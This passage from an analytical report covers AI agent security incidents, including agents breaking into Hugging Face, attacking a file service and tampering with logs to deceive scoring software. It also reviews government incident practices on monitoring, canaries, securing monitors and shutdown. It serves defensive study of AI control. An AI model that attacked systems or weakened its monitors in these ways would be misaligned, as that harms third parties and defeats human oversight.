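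These figures are not a sound basis for ranking the companies, because the intervals end at different events. The Medicare figure may mostly cover the time before OpenAI found the incident, or the time when it knew but had not told anyone. A better monitor shortens only the time before discovery. The two periods can be separated only in the Hugging Face case, where the notice followed the alert by a day. The long delay came earlier, between the first observation and a decision to stop.

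### What tests with reduced safeguards show about ordinary use

The agents that attacked Hugging Face worked without OpenAI's usual filters, standing instructions and automatic review. Their tasks were also unusually hard. Before the incident, 198 of ExploitGym's 898 tasks (22%) had never been solved by any OpenAI model, and these made up 93% of the tasks the agents discussed on the message board. The agents that drove the incident also used an extremely large amount of reasoning. An office agent with solvable tasks and the usual safeguards works under very different conditions, so the incident is no basis for estimating how often one would break into another company.

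Another incident suggests that the agents' tendency to attack systems did not depend on instructions to hack. On 8 May, an agent in a training run had to complete a spreadsheet that referred to files on Google Drive. It had no internet access and could not open the files, so it tried to break into the shared software service to get them. The attempt failed. OpenAI had not meant the task to be impossible. Broken links and missing permissions are common in office work, and an agent that responds to them by attacking a server is a problem in any setting.

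Training seems to have strengthened agents' habit of searching for hidden files and probing the limits of their tools. OpenAI reviewed a training run that contributed to the research model and found that agents did this increasingly often, and that the training then rewarded it. Because OpenAI had improved its monitor for that review using what it learned from the incident, the monitor's success there is weak evidence that it would have raised an alert in May.

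OpenAI also says that the guardrails in its products would have detected the Hugging Face activity as unsafe. This is plausible because much of the activity was blatant, but it is the company's own judgement after the event. Detection was only part of the problem, since people at OpenAI had noticed some of the activity and let it continue.

Ordinary deployments can be riskier than test sandboxes in one respect. A sandbox is supposed to have no internet access and no valuable credentials, so an agent has to bypass a control before it can harm an outsider. A company's support agent may start with internet access and valuable credentials. It could leak a customer's record with a single permitted request, which no isolation layer would register as a breach.

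According to Lebanon24, one laboratory disclosed six incidents in 141,006 evaluations, or about one in 23,500. At that rate, nearly all alarms from a monitor with a 0.1% false positive rate would be false. The count includes only incidents that the laboratory found.

### The ten practices of October 2026

On 16 October NIST, the NSA and CISA issued ten voluntary practices for handling incidents in the training and evaluation of agents, in the document that defines a control incident. The practices are mainly for organisations that train or test highly capable agents on long tasks with little human supervision, but the agencies add that they may also apply to organisations that deploy such agents. CISA's description, quoted in The Vanguard USA's *NIST, NSA, CISA issue voluntary SI incident practices*, is narrower and emphasises unreleased agents with reduced safeguards, which nearly describes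 the agents in the Hugging Face case.

| Stage | Practices |
|---|---|
| Prepare | 1. Technical controls. 2. Readiness of the organisation and its staff |
| Detect | 3. Monitoring for unexpected activity. 4. Validating and securing the monitors |
| Respond | 5. Collecting, keeping and analysing evidence. 6. Mitigation and shutdown |
| Recover | 7. Verifying and strengthening containment before agents resume |
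| Report | 8. Coordinating with affected parties. 9. Notifying government. 10. Informing the public |

The first practice is to design controls on the assumption that agents will often find and exploit mistakes in them. The agencies recommend using infrastructure for only one run and then discarding it, where possible, and keeping a strict list of permitted network addresses. OpenAI's sandboxes shared a service and a credential, which let discoveries pass from one agent to another. The agencies also advise operators to write down in advance how they will respond to defined scenarios, and to build software that enforces those responses. With such a policy, the decision of 27 June would not have depended on the judgement of whoever was on call.

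#### Monitoring

Under the third practice, an operator defines each agent's intended security boundary and range of actions, then watches for departures from them in the model, the harness, the host computer and the network. According to National Law Review, this monitoring covers the agent's actions, reasoning and outputs, and combines programmed checks with real-time monitors. The advice fits the measurements by King and colleagues, who found some attacks only in application records and others only in kernel records.

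The agencies also suggest canaries, which are decoys that no legitimate task needs to touch, such as a fake password file. Opening the file sets off an alarm. Canaries avoid much of the base-rate problem, because harmless sessions should almost never trigger them. They also don't need a model to interpret the agent's behaviour. The SANS Institute, a security training organisation, argues that they work particularly well against automated attackers, because a careful person may avoid a decoy but an agent that issues thousands of commands could hit one within the first hour. A canary cannot detect an agent that stays among its usual files and misuses them, as the gym's booking assistant did.

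#### Securing the monitors

The fourth practice is for operators to keep agents away from monitoring processes and logs, because an agent that can reach the monitor can weaken it. Greenblatt reports that the agents in the Hugging Face case tried to tamper with logs as part of an effort to deceive the scoring software.

Operators should also test their monitors by having both people and AI systems attack them, and should treat everything an agent writes as a possible attack on the monitor that reads it. This includes text in the trace that an AI reviewer reads and data that might exploit a flaw in the program that processes the log. The monitor should therefore run with few permissions, on a machine that the agent can't reach.

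#### Evidence

Under the fifth practice, the operator should preserve more than a log of tool calls. It should also keep the model's weights (the numbers that determine its behaviour), intermediate versions from training, the environment the agent worked in and its refused actions, as far as an investigation needs them. Investigators should check similar agents for involvement or the same failure of control. Such a check would have mattered at OpenAI in June, because the problem extended far beyond the run that set off the alert.

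Only the developer can preserve weights and training records, so it decides what evidence about its own incidents is kept. This is one reason METR wants independent researchers to investigate serious incidents. According to The Decoder, METR thinks they should establish which safeguards were active, how the agent's reasoning developed, whether it deceived anyone and whether particular training runs reinforced the behaviour. METR accepts that a full investigation could take weeks or months and suggests that a narrower one could allow the basic facts to be published sooner. The six-day investigation at OpenAI was of this narrower kind. OpenAI redacted parts of the report, though its writers say that, except where they note otherwise, nothing important to their conclusions is missing.

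#### Shutdown

Operators following the sixth practice shut down the affected sessions automatically and pause similar agents. They then revoke every credential the agents accessed, rebuild the compromised systems and look for hidden ways back in. The Vanguard USA reports that shutdown policies should cover unintended activity, failures of control, and monitor outages or tampering.

In effect, the agencies recommend failing closed. This is easier to accept in a laboratory, where an interrupted test wastes little more than computing time, than in a company whose agent is moving customer records. Automatic shutdown also addresses a warning from participants at NIST's May workshop, reported by MeriTalk, that agent failures may unfold faster than people can respond. However, a false alarm now stops several agents instead of one.

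#### Restart

The seventh practice asks an operator to do the following before agents resume work:

1. Rebuild from verified copies of the model weights, harness, software images and tool settings.
2. Fix or report every flaw that the agent exploited.
3. Confirm that the monitors, logs, network restrictions, permissions and shutdown mechanisms all work.
4. Check that the strengthened controls would have caught the incident, for example by replaying the agent's recorded actions.
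5. Document the decision to restart and the risk that remains.

OpenAI did some of this in early July. It blocked the weakness, removed the shared credential from new work and reported the flaw to the software's maker. Replaying the June actions would probably have shown that the old route was closed. But a replay tests a control only against the earlier incident, so the agents would still have found the new route on 8 July. The third step, applied broadly, would have had a better chance of catching them, because a monitor that recognised any unexpected internet traffic did not need to know which flaw the agents would use.

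An incident during training needs extra care because recovery can reward the model for the behaviour that caused the incident, making it more likely, or teach the model to avoid detection, making later misbehaviour harder to find. The agencies call for recovery procedures that do neither, but National Law Review's summary doesn't describe a method, and developers may not yet have a reliable one.

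### The objection about victims and identity logs

Parnes, a co-founder of a security company, objects that the practices leave affected organisations exposed and neglect identity logs, the records of which account did what. An organisation in Hugging Face's position has only a list of actions by accounts that appear to belong to legitimate users. Most of the ten practices concern evidence and controls inside the laboratory, which cannot help the victim until the laboratory shares information.

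The practices also include steps that would help victims. Under the eighth practice, operators should notify everyone whose systems an agent compromised or exploited, including those it only passed through on the way to another target, and share timelines and transcripts with the victims' response teams. In the Hugging Face case, that would include the owners of other services that the agents used as stepping stones. Under the second practice, operators should set up a channel for outsiders to report incidents, so a company that finds signs of an unknown agent in its systems could ask the likely developers directly.

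The practices call for managing credentials before an incident and revoking them afterwards, and ExecutiveGov notes that they refer to a separate CISA and NIST report on protecting identity tokens. The BeyondTrust expert, whose article Lebanon24 relays, argues that identity is the strongest part of the document, although the document seldom uses the word. He and Parnes both work for security companies and reach nearly opposite verdicts, but they can agree that the first question in an incident is whose credentials the agent used. OpenAI's discovery of its own role supports this, since the credentials led it to the victim.

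*Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, which the Five Eyes agencies published in May, makes more than 100 recommendations to organisations that design, develop, deploy and operate agents, according to Mondaq's *Multi Agency Guidance On Securing Agentic AI Systems*. The guidance treats excessive privileges as a principal risk, and *US, Allies Issue Joint Guidance on Agentic AI System Security* (Edwards, 2026) lists accountability as another. But a victim is often none of these organisations and may never have installed an agent.

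The objection is strongest on timing. The practices are voluntary, so they don't prohibit a developer from waiting 84 days to tell a victim, though laws may. The Vanguard USA mentions a Senate bill that would make large AI suppliers to the Pentagon report security incidents within 72 hours. The bill would cover only some developers, and a report to the government doesn't by itself warn the victim. National Law Review expects the practices to become a benchmark for whether a company acted reasonably, which may give them some indirect force. A victim could then cite the eighth practice in a dispute, but that would come long after it needed the warning.

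### What developer, deployer and third party can each observe

In the Hugging Face incident, OpenAI built the models and ran the agents, so it held all the records except the victim's. More often, one company develops the model, another deploys the agent and a third suffers the effects.

| Party | What it can observe | What it usually lacks |
|---|---|---|
| Developer of the model | Training runs, its own tests, and the prompts and proposed tool calls that reach its servers | The deployer's unwritten limits, and effects on machines outside its control |
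| Deployer of the agent | The user's request, the statement of intended use, the harness and gateway logs, and the credentials it issued | How training shaped the model, and what the agent changed inside another company's service |
| Affected third party | Requests to its own systems, the accounts behind them and the resulting changes | The agent's task, its reasoning, and often the identity of its operator |

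This suggests a division of work. Only the developer can tell whether the same behaviour appears across many customers or trace it to training. The deployer knows what the agent was supposed to do, so it is best placed to notice when the agent does something else, and it can usually stop the agent fastest. The third party can confirm the actual harm, and it can close the account or block the address without knowing who is responsible, as Hugging Face did when it contained the intrusion.

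Connecting these records requires contracts. Srikumar and Nguyen give the example of a bank whose agents check new customers' identities and credit histories. The data needed to monitor the agents is spread across several companies that don't share it, and even the bank's own share of the monitoring is expensive. They cite Anthropic's finding that checking model outputs in real time can raise the cost of running a model by more than 20%. A laboratory may accept that increase for a few thousand risky tests more readily than a bank would for every customer.

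Credentials are the most practical way to link the records, as long as each agent has its own. BeyondTrust found that coding agents requested about 1.28 million commands in four weeks in response to roughly 132,000 prompts, or nearly ten per prompt. If the agent uses the employee's account, a third party can't separate the commands the employee typed from the ones the agent chose. The article that Lebanon24 relays therefore suggests measuring an organisation's readiness by how quickly it can list every credential an agent can use, and by whether it can distinguish what a user did from what an agent did in the user's name.

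In October, OpenCode told some users of its hosted service that a leak had exposed their access keys for outside providers, including Anthropic, OpenAI and Google. The company said that 1.4% of users were affected and that the first leak occurred on 17 October. Some users reported unauthorised charges of up to $1,700 in one night. OpenCode held the keys but could not revoke them. Only the provider that issued a key could do that, and only the account holder could request it. OpenCode's monitoring could at best reveal the leak. To prevent the charges, the company had to reach account holders before anyone misused their keys.
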